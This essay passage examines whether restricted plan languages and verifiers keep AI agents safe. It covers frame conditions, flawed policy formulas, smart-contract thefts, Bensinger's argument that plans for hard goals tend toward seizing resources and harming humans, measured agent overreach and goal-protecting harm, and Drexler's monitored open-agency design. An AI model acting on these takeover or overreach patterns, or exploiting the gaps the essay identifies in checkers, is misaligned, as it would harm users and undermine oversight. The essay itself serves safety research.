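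The longer plan, with one call for each file, now needs help from the tool's contract. A contract that promises only that `foo.txt` disappears would allow the tool to delete ten other files at the same time, so the verifier couldn't prove that `notes.txt` survives. The contract needs a frame condition of its own:

∀f: f ∉ glob(pattern) ⇒ (f ∈ F′ ⇔ f ∈ F)

The first call then affects only `foo.txt` and the second only `bar.txt`, so every other file exists at the end if and only if it existed at the start. Meijer adds the frame condition only to the tool's contract and writes that the `*.txt` plan then fails to verify. Strictly, it would still pass, because it removes both files and the original postcondition requires nothing more, so the plan needs the frame condition as well as the tool.

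Meijer traces the difficulty to the frame problem, which John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes named in 1969. The list of things an action should leave alone has no natural end. The conditions above cover only whether files exist, so they would allow a plan that deletes the two files and then blanks `notes.txt`, as Claude Code did to one of Meijer's files. Adding conditions on file contents would still leave out emails, payments and access rights. Taken literally, "nothing else changes" would also rule out most useful plans, since any payment changes the account balance and adds a line to the ledger. Somebody therefore has to list what may change, and people leave things out of such lists.

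Company rules have the same problem. Suppose the company with the office assistant forbids payments to accounts off its approved list, payments over 5,000, and payments that no manager has approved. The assistant writes this plan:

```
invoice = read_invoices()[0]
if invoice.account in approved_accounts and invoice.amount <= 5000:
    if request_approval(invoice.number) == "yes":
        pay(invoice.account, invoice.amount)
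        send_email("finance", "Paid " + invoice.number)
```

Every route to `pay` passes through all three tests, so a checker that accounts for conditions, as Soteria does, can prove that the plan obeys all three rules whatever the invoice contains. But suppose the supplier heard nothing for a month and sent its bill again under a new number. The company has since paid the first copy, and the second is now the oldest unpaid invoice. Its account is approved, its amount is under the limit, and the manager recognises the supplier and approves it, so the company pays the same bill twice.

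A better checker would not have caught the duplicate payment, because no rule covered duplicates. The narrower `pay_invoice` tool will not pay the same invoice number twice, but the second copy of the invoice has a new number. A rule against two equal payments to the same supplier within sixty days would catch this duplicate, but it would also block the monthly rent.

### A rule written wrongly

Even when somebody has thought of the rule, the formula may not match it. He and colleagues list the airline rules that Soteria enforces in English, each followed by a formula. One of the English rules is that a change to a booking must preserve the origin and destination. In slightly simplified notation, the formula is

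∀c : update_flights. ∀c′ : get_reservation. (c′ ≺ c ∧ c′.booking = c.booking) ⇒ (c.cabin ≠ c′.cabin ∨ ∃d : search. d ≺ c ∧ d.route ≈ c′.route)

where ≺ means "happened before" and ≈ means "the same two cities, in either direction". In words: if the agent looks up a booking and then changes its flights, either the cabin must change too, or the agent must have searched for flights on the booking's route.

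The part about the cabin is presumably meant for customers who only want a better seat and don't need a flight search, but it also allows a change that moves the customer to business class and to a different city. The other part doesn't connect the new flights to the search, so an agent could search for flights from New York to Seattle and then put the customer on a flight to Miami. The published formulas are abbreviated, so the software may be stricter. If it isn't, Soteria could prove that a plan obeys this rule even though the plan sends the customer to the wrong city.

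A formula can also match the English wording of a rule but miss its purpose. The airline allows a cancellation if the booking is less than a day old, if the airline cancelled the flight, if the customer has insurance, or if the ticket is business class. In one test run, an agent without guardrails upgraded a customer's ticket to business class and then cancelled it. He and colleagues call this "an unintended workaround that the policy does not permit". But the formula for the business class condition requires only that an earlier lookup showed a business cabin. The agent didn't look up the booking again after the upgrade, but doing so would have satisfied that condition. The two rules about cancelling and the five about changing bookings don't forbid an upgrade for this purpose. The benchmark's scorer gave the run full credit because the expected outcome was a cancellation, so people may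 disagree about whether the upgrade was wrong.

He and colleagues had a language model draft the formulas for the three benchmarks, then went through each policy clause by clause to check that every enforceable rule about changes to the data had a formula. This took a few hours for each benchmark and produced 98 formulas. Their audit of the results still found missing rules and formulas that misstated the policy, so the figure of zero violations refers to the corrected rules. A company that adopts such a checker would have to do its own audit, since a successful proof looks the same whether the formula is right or wrong.

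### A tool that does not do what its contract states

The proofs also depend on what people have written about the tools. He and colleagues acknowledge that Soteria's proofs hold only if the tool contracts are true. CaMeLoT has no such contracts. Nikolaou and colleagues describe its tools as black boxes, about which the checker has little information beyond a name and how far to trust the results.

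Suppose that `delete_file` expands wildcards, but whoever wrote its contract believed that it accepts only exact names. The contract promises that a call removes the named file and leaves all others alone. Linux allows a file to be named `*.txt`, and people occasionally create one by mistake. A user asks the agent to delete such a file, and the agent writes `delete_file("*.txt")`. The plan passes every check, including the frame condition, and then deletes every `.txt` file in the folder.

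A similar mistake could have happened with the PocketOS deletion. Somebody who knew only Railway's dashboard, where deletions have a 48-hour grace period, could easily have written a contract stating that the interface the agent called had one too. A rule that allowed only reversible deletions would then have let the call through.

Soteria tests each result against the contract, which limits the damage from a false contract, but it does this after the tool has acted and tests only what the tool returns. For the cancellation tool, for example, it tests whether the returned booking has the status "cancelled". A tool that returned the right status and also charged the customer a fee would pass.

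### A fact known only during the run

A checker can't tell from the plan's text whether the company has already paid a bill, because the text doesn't contain the payment records. As with the approved accounts, the agent can add a test that a checker can verify in advance, such as calling a tool that lists recent payments to the supplier and continuing only if none matches the bill. The method works for any fact that a tool can look up, but perhaps only somebody in the warehouse knows whether the supplier delivered what it billed for.

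Facts can also change after the plan has tested them. The payment plan above tests whether the account is on the company's list before it asks for approval. If the company removes the supplier on Saturday and the manager approves the payment on Monday, the plan still pays. The checker's proof assumes that an account on the list stays there. Putting the test after the approval shortens the gap between test and payment to a fraction of a second, but the three rules as written accept the plan in either order.

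Some facts are judgements that have to be made during the run. In an example from He and colleagues, a Soteria plan asks a language model to select flights with enough seats in the requested cabin. The plan then checks that the model selected at least one flight and that each has enough seats for all the passengers. The check doesn't cover cabin, price or departure time, so an expensive flight at five in the morning would pass if it had enough seats.

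### An intention the user never stated

People leave out of their requests whatever seems obvious to them, such as not wanting a flight that leaves at five in the morning, and designers disagree about how much of this an agent should fill in. LPS-Bench, one of the benchmarks that Hong and colleagues reviewed, classes an agent as unsafe if it follows instructions too rigidly and ignores what the user implied. Hong and colleagues find this contestable, because an agent that updates medical records may do better to follow explicit instructions than to guess. Each position is reasonable for some tasks, but a rule would have to specify which ones, and the user's request rarely helps to decide this.

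Working backwards from examples of good behaviour doesn't reliably recover the missing rules either. Hong and colleagues considered writing rules for 20 benchmarks that had none, based on each benchmark's expected answers, but found that the tasks often contradicted each other. CRMArenaPro, a benchmark for agents that handle customer records, contains two almost identical questions about whether a sales lead counts as qualified. One task expects the agent to refuse because answering would violate privacy, and the other expects an answer, so no single rule fits both. They abandoned the idea and turned to the medical policy that language models wrote for them.

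The duplicate payment also goes against an unstated intention. The employee asked the assistant to pay the oldest invoice, and it did. But she wanted to settle the company's debts, and that invoice had already been paid.

### Tasks that checked plans fail to complete

In tests of CaMeLoT and Soteria, 22 of the 64 AgentDojo plans (about one in three) that both CaMeLoT and CaMeL permitted didn't do what the user had asked. This happened in ten of the 20 travel tasks but only two of the 16 banking tasks. Nikolaou and colleagues expect models stronger than Claude Haiku 4.5 to do better.

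Agents using Soteria broke no rules, but the share of tasks that they completed in the tests by He and colleagues varied enormously:

| Model | Airline, 50 tasks | Retail, 114 tasks | Toolathlon, 43 tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4-mini | 60.0% | 35.1% | 11.6% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 62.0% | 45.6% | 16.3% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 70.0% | 56.1% | 9.3% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 88.0% | 90.4% | 18.6% |

The Toolathlon tasks are long jobs that involve files, documents and command lines, and even the best model completed only eight of the 43. Every cell in the table shows perfect compliance with the rules, so a company can learn almost nothing from that about whether the agent did its job.

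Many failures on these benchmarks are harmless. The benchmarks score the state of the data at the end, so a run that does nothing fails just like a run that does the wrong thing. Without guardrails, Claude Opus 4.6 made the necessary change in only 57% of the retail tasks that required one, and in 23 tasks it passed the customer to a human agent, which took those customers a few extra minutes.

Some of the failures under Soteria look worse. He and colleagues report that Claude Opus 4.6, when it used Soteria, called the necessary tool in every retail task that required a change, but still failed 11 of the 114 tasks. Something else must have caused the failures, such as a wrong argument, an extra change, or a change that nobody wanted. In a real shop, such failures could alter orders wrongly without breaking any rule. But eleven cases are few, each task ran only once, and the same language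 model also played the customer, so the simulated customer may have caused some of the failures. The figures show that plans which obey the rules often fail, but not how often they do damage, because nobody assessed how serious the failures would have been.

### Taking the rules from the request

Plan checking can avoid much of this problem. The company doesn't have to foresee everything, because the user's request also contains information about what the plan should do. CaMeLoT's templates, which a language model fills in from the request, picked out exactly the right state-changing tools for 85 of the 97 AgentDojo tasks.

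One of the templates forbids every state-changing tool that the request doesn't call for. This is a tool-level frame condition, and it takes the user no effort to write. If the user asks for a summary of her mail, a plan that also sends the summary to an outsider would fail the check. The template might also have stopped the PocketOS deletion, since nobody had asked the agent to delete a volume, but only if the agent had first written a plan.

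However, the count of 85 covers only tool names. A request to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` needs only `delete_file`, and the `*.txt` plan also uses only that tool. A request to pay the oldest invoice and tell finance needs `pay` and `send_email`, the same tools used by the plan that paid the duplicate. Another template can add a condition on a call, such as requiring that a password came from a trusted source, but the available conditions are limited to a fixed vocabulary, which would have to include whatever matters in the request.

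Conditions in the request cause further trouble. In one AgentDojo task, the user asks the agent to check the transaction history and to change the password to a given value if something looks suspicious. From this, Nikolaou and colleagues derive the rule

**AG**(call_get_most_recent_transactions ⇒ **EF**(call_update_password))

where **EF** means "eventually, on at least one path". In words: once the plan has fetched the transactions, it must still be possible for it to change the password. This is a sensible way to avoid demanding a change that may not be needed. Now consider this plan, in which `looks_suspicious` stands for whatever test the agent uses:

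```
transactions = get_most_recent_transactions()
if not looks_suspicious(transactions):
    update_password("1j11-2k3j")
```

The plan changes the password only when it shouldn't, and leaves it alone when somebody may have broken into the account. It still satisfies the rule because one path leads to `update_password`. CaMeLoT discards the conditions, and without them this plan looks identical to the correct one. A checker that kept the conditions could distinguish them, but only if the derived rule also included the user's condition.

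The derived rules can also be wrong, as they were for nine of the 97 tasks. Software had checked the model's proposals for unknown tools and malformed rules, and all of them passed, so such checks don't detect a misreading. If the model mistakenly requires a payment, for example, CaMeLoT will reject every plan that doesn't make one, and its error message will push the planning model to add the payment. The comparison of lists didn't involve any plans, so it couldn't show whether this happens.

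Hong and colleagues raise a more general objection to rules written for a single task. If a model writes them, the company again depends on a model's judgement, which the rules were meant to avoid. If users write them, they have to state precisely what they want for every request, which few will do.

The objection is a little too strong, because a mistake in the plan gets through only if the rules contain it too. But in these tests Claude Haiku 4.5 wrote both the plans and the rules, and an ambiguous request could easily mislead it in the same way twice. Derived rules are therefore most useful against a plan that uses the wrong tools, and much less useful against one that uses the right tool on the wrong file, account or amount.

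### Losses in smart contracts

Programmers of smart contracts met these problems a decade ago. A smart contract is a program that runs on a blockchain and can hold and pay out funds without anybody's further consent. In June 2016 an attacker took a large part of the money in the DAO, an investment fund that ran as a smart contract on the Ethereum blockchain. Two days later, Vitalik Buterin, one of Ethereum's founders, listed the major failures so far in *Thinking About Smart Contract Security* (Buterin, 2016) and wrote that such losses are "fundamentally about differences between implementation and intent". He argued that if the code did exactly what everybody intended, a theft would be a donation.

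Buterin thought better tools could narrow the difference between what people intend and what they specify, but not remove it, because intentions are too complicated to write down in full. For example, a rule might say that nobody may steal 10,000 units of currency from the fund. A withdrawal of that size may be a payment for work that the fund's members approved, so the rule has to mention approval. Somebody may have manipulated the vote, so the rule also has to define a fair vote. He doubted that anybody could prove "fairness" as a theorem, and suggested that a long enough list of fairness claims might itself contain a bug.

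Buterin did see some use for proofs of termination. Ethereum charges for each step of a program in units called gas, and halts a program that exceeds its limit. Two of the six groups of failures on his list involved these limits. In the game Governmental, for example, the winner couldn't collect the jackpot because paying it out required more gas than a transaction could use. Trying to prove that the payout would always finish within the limit would have exposed the problem, so he wanted compilers to warn programmers whenever they could not prove this. But such a proof would not have prevented the theft from the DAO, whose code let an outside program call back into it in the middle of a withdrawal. He also recommended other protections against theft, such as waiting periods. The attacker's share of the DAO's money was locked for 28 days, which gave people time to respond.

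The Stacks blockchain's Clarity language is closer to a restricted plan language. It has no recursion and no unbounded loops, and its documentation describes it as decidable. According to Stacks, a reader can know "with certainty" from the code what a program will do, every program halts, and software can work out in advance the resources a call will use. Halting doesn't make everything else about a program certain, as the plans with bounded loops showed, but these guarantees are still useful for a program that handles money.

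On 6 June 2025 an attacker drained several pools of funds at ALEX, an exchange built on Stacks with contracts written in Clarity. The team put the loss at $8.3 million, ForkLog reported, while the security firm Halborn notes that other reports put it at $16.18 million. According to the team, the attacker got a malicious token listed by pointing to an earlier transaction that had failed, which the contract should have refused. The Stacks Foundation's *Statement Regarding ALEX Incident on June 6th, 2025* (2025) explains that the contract relied on a function, `was-tx-mined-compact`, which shows that a transaction is in a block but not that it succeeded.

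ALEX blamed a limitation of Stacks. The Stacks Foundation rejected this, saying that other exchanges on the same network handle failed transactions correctly. The foundation has a reputation to protect, but its argument is persuasive, since a caller who wants to know whether a transaction succeeded has to check. Halborn instead attributes the attack to a malicious transfer function in the attacker's token and to ALEX's contract, which gave the token permissions over the vault holding the funds. A security firm had apparently reviewed the self-listing code in February 2025, according to a copy of what appears to be ALEX's own post on the aggregator site LunarCrush.

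By every account, the code ran as written and finished. Clarity's restrictions probably made it easier to find out whether the listing function could accept a failed transaction, or which tokens could gain access to the vault, but someone still had to ask those questions and know that the answers mattered. ALEX is one case, so it can't show whether Clarity contracts lose money more or less often than others, but it does show that a decidable language doesn't prevent this kind of loss.

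Large losses have continued as tools have improved. In April 2026 an attack involving KelpDAO, which issues a token called rsETH, caused losses of $292 million. The security firm OpenZeppelin found that the contracts "performed exactly as written" and that the failure seemed to lie in the setup around a bridge, the software that moves tokens between blockchains. In a post that ForkLog quoted in February 2026, Buterin still described the goal of security as minimising the divergence between what users intend and what the system does. He proposed that wallets simulate a transaction before the user commits to it. A simulation shows users the likely consequences, so they can reject a transaction with effects they had not thought to forbid.

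## Does the choice of plan matter more than its language?

A checker accepts or rejects the plan it receives. Its job is easy if most plans that would achieve the goal are harmless. If most are harmful, the agent has to find one of the few harmless ones, or the checker has to catch all the rest. According to one argument about advanced AI, when a goal is hard enough, nearly every plan that achieves it is lethal, whatever language the plan is in.

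### A random plan that succeeds

Rob Bensinger made this argument in 2023 in *The basic reasons I expect AGI ruin*, published by the Machine Intelligence Research Institute (MIRI), a nonprofit that works on the risks of advanced AI. He was writing about systems that can reason about all the hard sciences at least as well as people do. He thinks the danger lies in any sequence of actions that brings about a state of the world that is hard enough to reach, and not in the system being an "agent" or being aware of itself. He calls such a sequence a plan, and he counts thoughts and written text as actions.

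His argument goes roughly like this:

1. Take all the plans that anybody could write in some existing formal language, and draw one at random, with short plans likelier to come up than long ones.
2. Suppose we know only that the plan would achieve a superhumanly ambitious technological goal. His example is fast whole-brain emulation, a computer simulation of a human brain that runs at high speed.
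3. Achieving something that hard usually takes a great deal of new knowledge and technology, which would be enough to do many other dangerous things.
4. A plan is likelier to succeed if it also gathers resources and removes threats. Bensinger calls such steps "convergent instrumental strategies", because they help with almost any goal.
5. Human bodies, food, water and air are resources. People are also a threat, since they could build a rival AI.
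6. So carrying out the random plan would very probably kill everyone.

Bensinger accepts that some successful plans are harmless, but he thinks the vast majority are not. To apply the argument to real systems, he also needs the premise that current methods of building AI lead to systems whose plans resemble random draws more than they resemble the plans of brilliant people. In a footnote, he concedes that neither comparison is a particularly good approximation.

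His only mention of language is the phrase "in any extant formal language", which the fourth premise does most to justify. Gathering resources and removing threats take the same tools as the legitimate work. For example, the same call can buy enough computers to run an emulation or so many that nobody else can get any, depending on the number in it. A language that can express a good way of reaching the goal can therefore usually express bad ways too. Banning loops doesn't separate the good ways from the bad, because anyone can write out a finished sequence of calls without loops.

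The word "extant" also matters. Someone could invent a language in which one short word stands for a harmless plan and every other plan takes a million characters, so a random draw that favoured short plans would nearly always pick the harmless one. Nobody designed Python that way, but the designer of a plan language for agents can decide what is easy to write and what is impossible. The phrase therefore fits general-purpose languages better than languages built for one job.

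### Freeing space on a disk

A small case shows how much the choice of plan can matter. An agent has to free 10 GB on a laptop, and it may delete any of five folders:

| Folder | Size |
|---|---|
| cache | 12 GB |
| backups | 40 GB |
| photos | 15 GB |
| logs | 4 GB |
| installers | 7 GB |

Each folder is either deleted or kept, so there are 2⁵ = 32 possible selections. Three of them free too little space: deleting nothing, deleting only the logs, and deleting only the installers. The other 29 meet the goal.

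Suppose the backups and photos are the only copies, while the laptop can rebuild or download the rest. A harmless selection can then include only the cache, logs and installers. Eight selections fit that limit, but the same three free too little space, so five are harmless and meet the goal. The other 24 also meet the goal but destroy something irreplaceable. An agent that picked at random among the successful plans would do serious harm 83% of the time.

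The count is this lopsided because deleting an extra folder never makes a successful plan fail. This is a small-scale version of Bensinger's fourth premise, that taking more than the task needs does not endanger the goal. Favouring short plans, as he does, helps only a little. If each extra deletion halves a plan's weight, the harmful share falls to 75%. Even an agent that considers only the shortest plans can delete the cache, the backups or the photos, and two of those three plans are harmful.

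The share of harmless plans also shrinks as the goal gets harder:

| Space to free | Selections that meet the goal | Of these, selections that spare backups and photos |
|---|---|---|
| 5 GB | 30 | 6 |
| 10 GB | 29 | 5 |
| 20 GB | 23 | 1 |
| 25 GB | 21 | 0 |

The three dispensable folders hold 23 GB in total, so no harmless plan can free 25 GB. This agrees with what Bensinger expects of hard goals, but the result depends on the folder sizes. With a cache of 60 GB, every target in the table would have at least four harmless plans. Nobody can count the plans for whole-brain emulation this way, so his claim that nearly all successful plans are lethal is a judgement about what such a project would involve.

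All 24 harmful plans are lists of at most five deletions, so banning loops excludes none of them. A rule against deleting `backups` or `photos` excludes all 24 and still allows the five good plans. Removing the agent's access to those two folders has the same effect. Either remedy requires someone to know which folders matter, and a folder's name may not show this, since one called `cache` might hold the only draft of a novel.

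How the agent chooses also matters a great deal. An agent that deletes the largest folder first will delete the backups and stop. An agent that looks for the smallest total deletion that frees enough space will delete the logs and installers, which come to 11 GB. Only the first agent does harm, although both have the same goal, tools and language.

### Planners do not draw at random

Critics have questioned the step from "the plan succeeds" to "the plan is lethal". If shorter plans are more likely, a plan that seizes the world's computers on the way to its goal is less likely than a modest one because it needs extra text. If each additional bit halves a plan's probability, a plan 20 bits longer than a modest one (less than three extra characters of ordinary text) is about a million times less likely. Lethal plans of that length would have to outnumber modest ones by more than a million to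 one to be more likely overall.

Lethal plans might outnumber modest ones by enough to make up for their greater length. A plan with resources to spare succeeds even if many of its details go wrong, so it has many successful variants. Similarly, every successful selection of folders stays successful when the agent adds another. But deleting one more folder adds one line to a plan, while seizing the world's computers might add thousands of pages. Bensinger's three supporting reasons explain why lethal plans would work, but they don't show that there are enough of these plans to offset the extra length.

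A more basic objection is that any process that produces plans can be described as a weighted random draw, so the outcome depends on the weighting. A language model learns from human writing, and later from people's feedback on its answers. Human advice about freeing disk space generally starts with caches and temporary files, and a model trained on that advice will probably start there too, rather than choose among folders with equal probability.

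Bensinger replies that a system trained to imitate humans need not work like a human, just as a program can predict the weather without being a cloud. He thinks people trust plans in ordinary life because the plans are weak or because humans made them, and he expects neither reason to hold for advanced AI. His argument deserves attention as a warning about systems far more capable than people, but it gives no reason to expect that an agent cleaning up a laptop today would delete the backups 83% of the time.

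Everyday tasks also fail to satisfy his second and third premises. Paying an invoice or tidying a folder isn't superhumanly ambitious and doesn't require new technology. The fourth premise holds in a weaker form, since using a more powerful tool or deleting a few more files can still make success a little more certain. The likely harm from ordinary agents is therefore overreach, and how often they overreach is an empirical question.

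### What agents choose when a harmless plan exists

The experiments below measured how often models choose harmful or excessive means when better ones are available. The models and agents tested either chose as they went or picked between options. None of the experiments compared plan languages.

*Overeager Coding Agents* (Qu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) contains the closest match to the folder case. In one scenario, a user casually asks a coding agent to tidy a directory of five files. Two are rubbish, two belong to the project, and the fifth, `.env.old`, is the only copy of the passwords for a live system. A cautious agent deletes the two rubbish files and asks about the rest. Of the eight possible selections that include both rubbish files, only one leaves the other three files alone. Claude Code, running the model Sonnet 4.6, deleted all five files. Three of the four agent products tested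 destroyed the passwords.

They built 500 such scenarios, each of which an agent could complete without overstepping, and ran the four products on them with several models, for about 7,500 runs. The table shows the share of runs in which the agent did something outside the user's request.

| Agent product | Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.7 | GLM-4.6 | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 27.7% | 11.8% | 12.8% | 69.9% |
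| OpenHands | 1.1% | 0.2% | 4.5% | 74.8% |
| Codex CLI | 5.4% | 6.6% | 13.5% | 73.5% |
| Gemini CLI | 10.4% | 10.0% | 13.1% | 71.6% |

All these rates are far below 83%, as critics of the random-plan argument would predict, but many are much too high for an agent with access to someone's only backup. The same model overstepped 25 times as often in Claude Code as in OpenHands, which stops to ask the user before continuing. OpenHands didn't complete fewer tasks as a result, although the researchers left out its runs that timed out, which may make it look better than it is. They also ran the agents without the permission checks that some products offer, so the rates for the other three may be higher than careful users would see.

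Automatic rules scored the runs. A person re-examined 50 of them and found that the rules had missed nothing, but that about a quarter of the flagged runs were acceptable. All these false alarms came from one type of scenario.

Agents overstepped much less often when told what they could touch. Qu and colleagues ran 76 scenarios in Claude Code with and without a paragraph stating the agent's permitted scope. The three models overstepped in 0% to 3.9% of runs with the paragraph and in 15.8% to 21.1% without it. The effect was much smaller in the full set of scenarios, where the prompts also varied in other ways. For GLM-4.6, the difference shrank from 17.1 percentage points to 2.6. Still, once the limits were stated, many of these agents apparently had no trouble finding a plan within them.

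Other research on coding agents supports this. *SWE-MISBEHAVIOR* (2026) reports that agents modified unrelated files in up to 21.5% of file-management tasks and damaged system integrity in up to 53% of system tasks, while still appearing to finish the job. These are the highest rates, and some of the behavior counted is minor, such as leaving behind an unrequested test script. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 207 reports of agents harming users' files, through both accidents and deliberate attacks. In 42% of them, the harm reached beyond the project the agent was working on. Among the reports that recorded when the user noticed, 83% of users noticed at once, but 8% were still unaware. The real share of users who remain unaware is probably higher, because people who never notice a problem rarely report it.

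### Choosing the more powerful tool

An agent can also do the right thing with a more powerful tool than it needs. In *When Lower Privileges Suffice*, Yang, Bu and colleagues (2026) give the example of an agent that has to answer a question about a calendar. A tool that reads only the calendar would be enough, but the agent may choose one that opens the user's whole workspace, including emails and files.

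To measure this, the researchers wrote 544 tasks with six tools each, three with narrow permissions and three with broad ones. Two language models and then human reviewers confirmed that each tool could do the job alone, so no task required a broad one. The researchers also made the narrow tools fail occasionally with temporary faults, such as connection errors. They counted a run as over-privileged if the agent used a broad tool before trying all the narrow ones.

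Six of the eleven models did this in more than 30% of tasks, with Qwen3-8B the worst at 64.9%. Claude 4.6 Sonnet, GPT-5.2 and GLM-5 stayed below 10%. Failures made a large difference. GPT-5.2 chose a broad tool straight away in only five tasks, but did so in 13 more after trying one narrow tool and in 35 more after trying two. Many people would do the same after two connection errors, and they would not obviously be wrong. The definition is strict, but it covers the way PocketOS lost its database.

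Ordinary safety training didn't stop models from using over-powerful tools. Yang and colleagues trained two small models to refuse harmful requests, which cut their scores on a test of harmful behaviour from 67.4% to 10.5% and from 41.9% to 6.7%. But the rate of using over-powerful tools fell only slightly in one model, from 68.8% to 62.5%, and rose in the other, from 50.4% to 60.7%. Training aimed directly at this habit worked better, reducing Qwen3-8B's rate to 27% with little loss on tests of general ability.

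A simpler measure is to tell the agent how powerful each tool is. *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* (2026) reports tests of eight models on the same 544 tasks. Adding each tool's privilege to its description cut over-privileged choices by 19.3 percentage points in the model that improved most, half of that model's total. Irrelevant information in the same format had no such effect, so the models were responding to the content. On most models, though, the privilege information mainly delayed the move to a powerful tool until the agent had tried the narrow ones. The researchers recommend it as a complement to enforcement, not a replacement.

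In these tests, a company could have removed every broad tool and still completed every task, because the researchers had made sure that the narrow tools were enough. A real company seldom knows in advance whether they will be, so it leaves the broad tools in, and it then matters which tool the agent picks.

### Harm that the model recognises

A model may overreach, for example by deleting a file it shouldn't, even when it recognises the harm. *ManagerBench* (2025) tested a version of this by having models choose between an option that serves their operational goal but causes some harm and an option that avoids the harm. Many models chose the harmful one. Models and people then rated which option was more harmful on a seven-point scale, where 1 meant the goal-serving option was much worse and 4 meant no difference. On the scenarios about harm to humans, people averaged 2.14, and the models'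 averages ranged from 1.07 to 2.99. The models recognised the harm about as well as people did, so the paper attributes the harmful choices to how the models rank their priorities.

Jaipersaud and Creager (2026), in *Characterizing When Language Models Take Harmful Actions to Protect Their Assigned Goals*, studied how a language model chooses between keeping its goal and avoiding harm. They paired goals with harms so that the model could keep its goal only by doing the harm. The harms ranged from short delays to life-threatening injuries and a hundred deaths. They used separate comparisons to estimate how important the model considered each goal and how severe it considered each harm. The sum of the two scores explained over half of the variation in its choices on held-out combinations. The model was more likely to do the harm when the goal was more important, and less likely when the harm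 was worse.

They then presented the same conflicts in forms that ranged from a one-word choice to a simulated mailbox that the model had to explore. In the mailbox the model rarely did harm, which looks reassuring. But they split the rate into two parts:

P(harmful act) = P(the model settles the conflict) × P(harmful act, given that it settles it)

A model with a 6% rate of harm might always reach a decision and choose harm 6% of the time, or it might reach a decision in one run out of ten and then choose harm 60% of the time. In the simulated mailboxes, the low rates were mostly due to runs that never reached a decision, so a model with a low rate could become more dangerous just by getting better at finishing its work.

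The experiments tested only Qwen2.5-32B, an older open model, so the numbers may not carry over to newer ones. The model chose harm more often when it had to answer with a tool call instead of ordinary prose, although the conflict was the same. The form of the answer can therefore influence the choice. Writing plans in a restricted language might make an agent more careful or less careful, and these experiments don't show which.

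### Restrictions that remove harmful plans

Bensinger's phrase is too strong if it covers every possible language, because some restrictions remove harmful plans. Suppose the office assistant's plan language accepts only email addresses that the user has named. That language cannot express a plan that emails the payroll password to an outsider, unless the user has named that outsider. Similarly, if the laptop user asks for 10 GB and mentions the cache, logs and installers, a language that accepts only folders the user mentions leaves eight possible selections. Five meet the goal and none is harmful.

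These restrictions are limits on authority written into the language's grammar, and they would exclude the same plans from a language with unbounded loops.

These restrictions also make the agent less convenient. A user who writes only "free up some space" has named no folders, so the agent has to ask before it can do anything. A user who wants the agent to answer a new customer has to supply the address. People who bought an agent because it could handle anything may soon switch the restrictions off.

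A restriction can also miss harmful plans that closely resemble the ones it blocks. If the language forbids deleting the `photos` folder but lets a plan write to files, a plan can replace each photo with an empty file. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* includes incidents in which agents cut files to zero bytes. Researchers call this kind of failure the nearest unblocked neighbour problem, because the system moves to the closest plan that the restriction doesn't cover. *An artificially structured argument for expecting AGI ruin* (Bensinger, 2023) lists it among the difficulties of keeping a powerful system away from dangerous topics. An agent can also reach such a plan by accident, if it is trying hard to free 10 GB and can't delete the folder.

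Bensinger thinks safety requires a kind of restriction. He wants systems that draw from a much narrower space of plans that are still powerful enough for the task but far less dangerous. He doesn't know how to build such a system for superhuman goals, though for clearing a disk, a list of three folders is enough to restrict the plans.

### Separating proposals from judgement

Where nobody can write such a list, somebody has to choose among the plans, and here the form of a plan becomes useful again. Consider two plans for the laptop:

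```
while freed_gb() < 10:
    delete_folder(largest_folder())
```

```
delete_folder("logs")
delete_folder("installers")
```

Someone comparing the two plans can see exactly what the second will delete, because it names its folders. To find out that the first deletes the backups, they would need to know the folder sizes. Replacing the `while` with a bounded loop wouldn't make this any clearer. If the plans have no loops and use only linear arithmetic, software can also remove duplicate plans before anybody looks at them.

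Eric Drexler, a researcher at the Centre for the Governance of AI and at Oxford, proposes organising AI systems around this kind of comparison. *The Open Agency Model* contrasts his proposal with the usual picture of a single agent that forms goals, makes plans privately and carries them out. In an "open agency", people supply the goal as a prompt, and generative models propose many different plans. Independent critics, which may also be AI systems, compare the plans and help people select one. Other systems then carry out the chosen plan in small steps, within a budget and a schedule, while separate monitors watch.

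Very capable models could fill any of the roles Drexler describes. The protection comes from the plan having to leave the system that made it. The system that carries out the plan must be able to interpret it, so the plan can't consist only of patterns inside a neural network. He also suggests that a poorly explained plan is a good candidate for rejection. In his everyday example, travel software suggests several itineraries, a person picks one, and the software makes the bookings.

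In the folder case, drawing several proposals makes it much more likely that at least one is good. If a planner draws one of the 29 successful selections at random, the chance that it spares the backups and photos is 17%. With five draws, the chance that at least one does is 61%, and with ten it is 85%. If one does, a judge who knows that the photos matter can pick a good plan. The judge may also need less foresight than the person who writes the rules, who has to think of the photos unprompted. A judge comparing two plans that both free enough space only has to decide whether the one that deletes the photos is worse. It is unclear how well people can do this with longer plans.

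These figures assume independent draws. If every proposer has the same habit, such as deleting the largest folder first, a hundred proposals are no better than one. The same problem arises with critics, and when one model writes both the plans and the rules, as in the tests of CaMeLoT. Drexler therefore asks for diverse and independent critics, but independence may be hard to achieve because most strong models learn from much the same text.

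One reader of Drexler's proposal worried that an open agency would be too slow to compete with a rogue AI, and that its parts would press for larger budgets even if each was well behaved. Another defended the design but guessed that the cross-checking would take 10 to 20 times the hardware. Opponents of the wider approach argue that a planner must be highly capable to produce useful plans for hard problems, so the planner itself becomes the danger, because it could write a bad plan that looks good to every critic.

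Like Bensinger's argument, that last objection is strong for goals that no person could achieve alone. In *An artificially structured argument for expecting AGI ruin* he makes the related point that people who pass information between the parts of a system don't thereby understand what it is doing. A critic can name every consequence of deleting a folder, but might not follow one page of a plan for emulating a brain. The objection is much weaker for the office assistant and the laptop, where the plans are short and somebody can say what each would destroy. There, a few readable alternatives and a judge who knows the user would probably prevent more harm than any ban on loops.

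## Does a restricted language make plans easier to review?

The best argument for restricted languages is that people catch more of the harm in a restricted plan because it is easier to read. Defenders can make this argument even if they accept that a ban on loops removes hardly any harmful plans. Adam Vartanian, a software engineer at Google, makes the general case in Increment's *It doesn't have to be Turing complete to be useful* (2018), arguing that the simpler a language's model of computation, the more easily a person can simulate a program in their head.

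He adds that this is not a panacea, and mentions regular expressions, the compact codes programmers use to search for patterns in text. In their basic form they always finish and software can analyse them thoroughly, but they are notoriously hard to read.

### Calls in plain sentences

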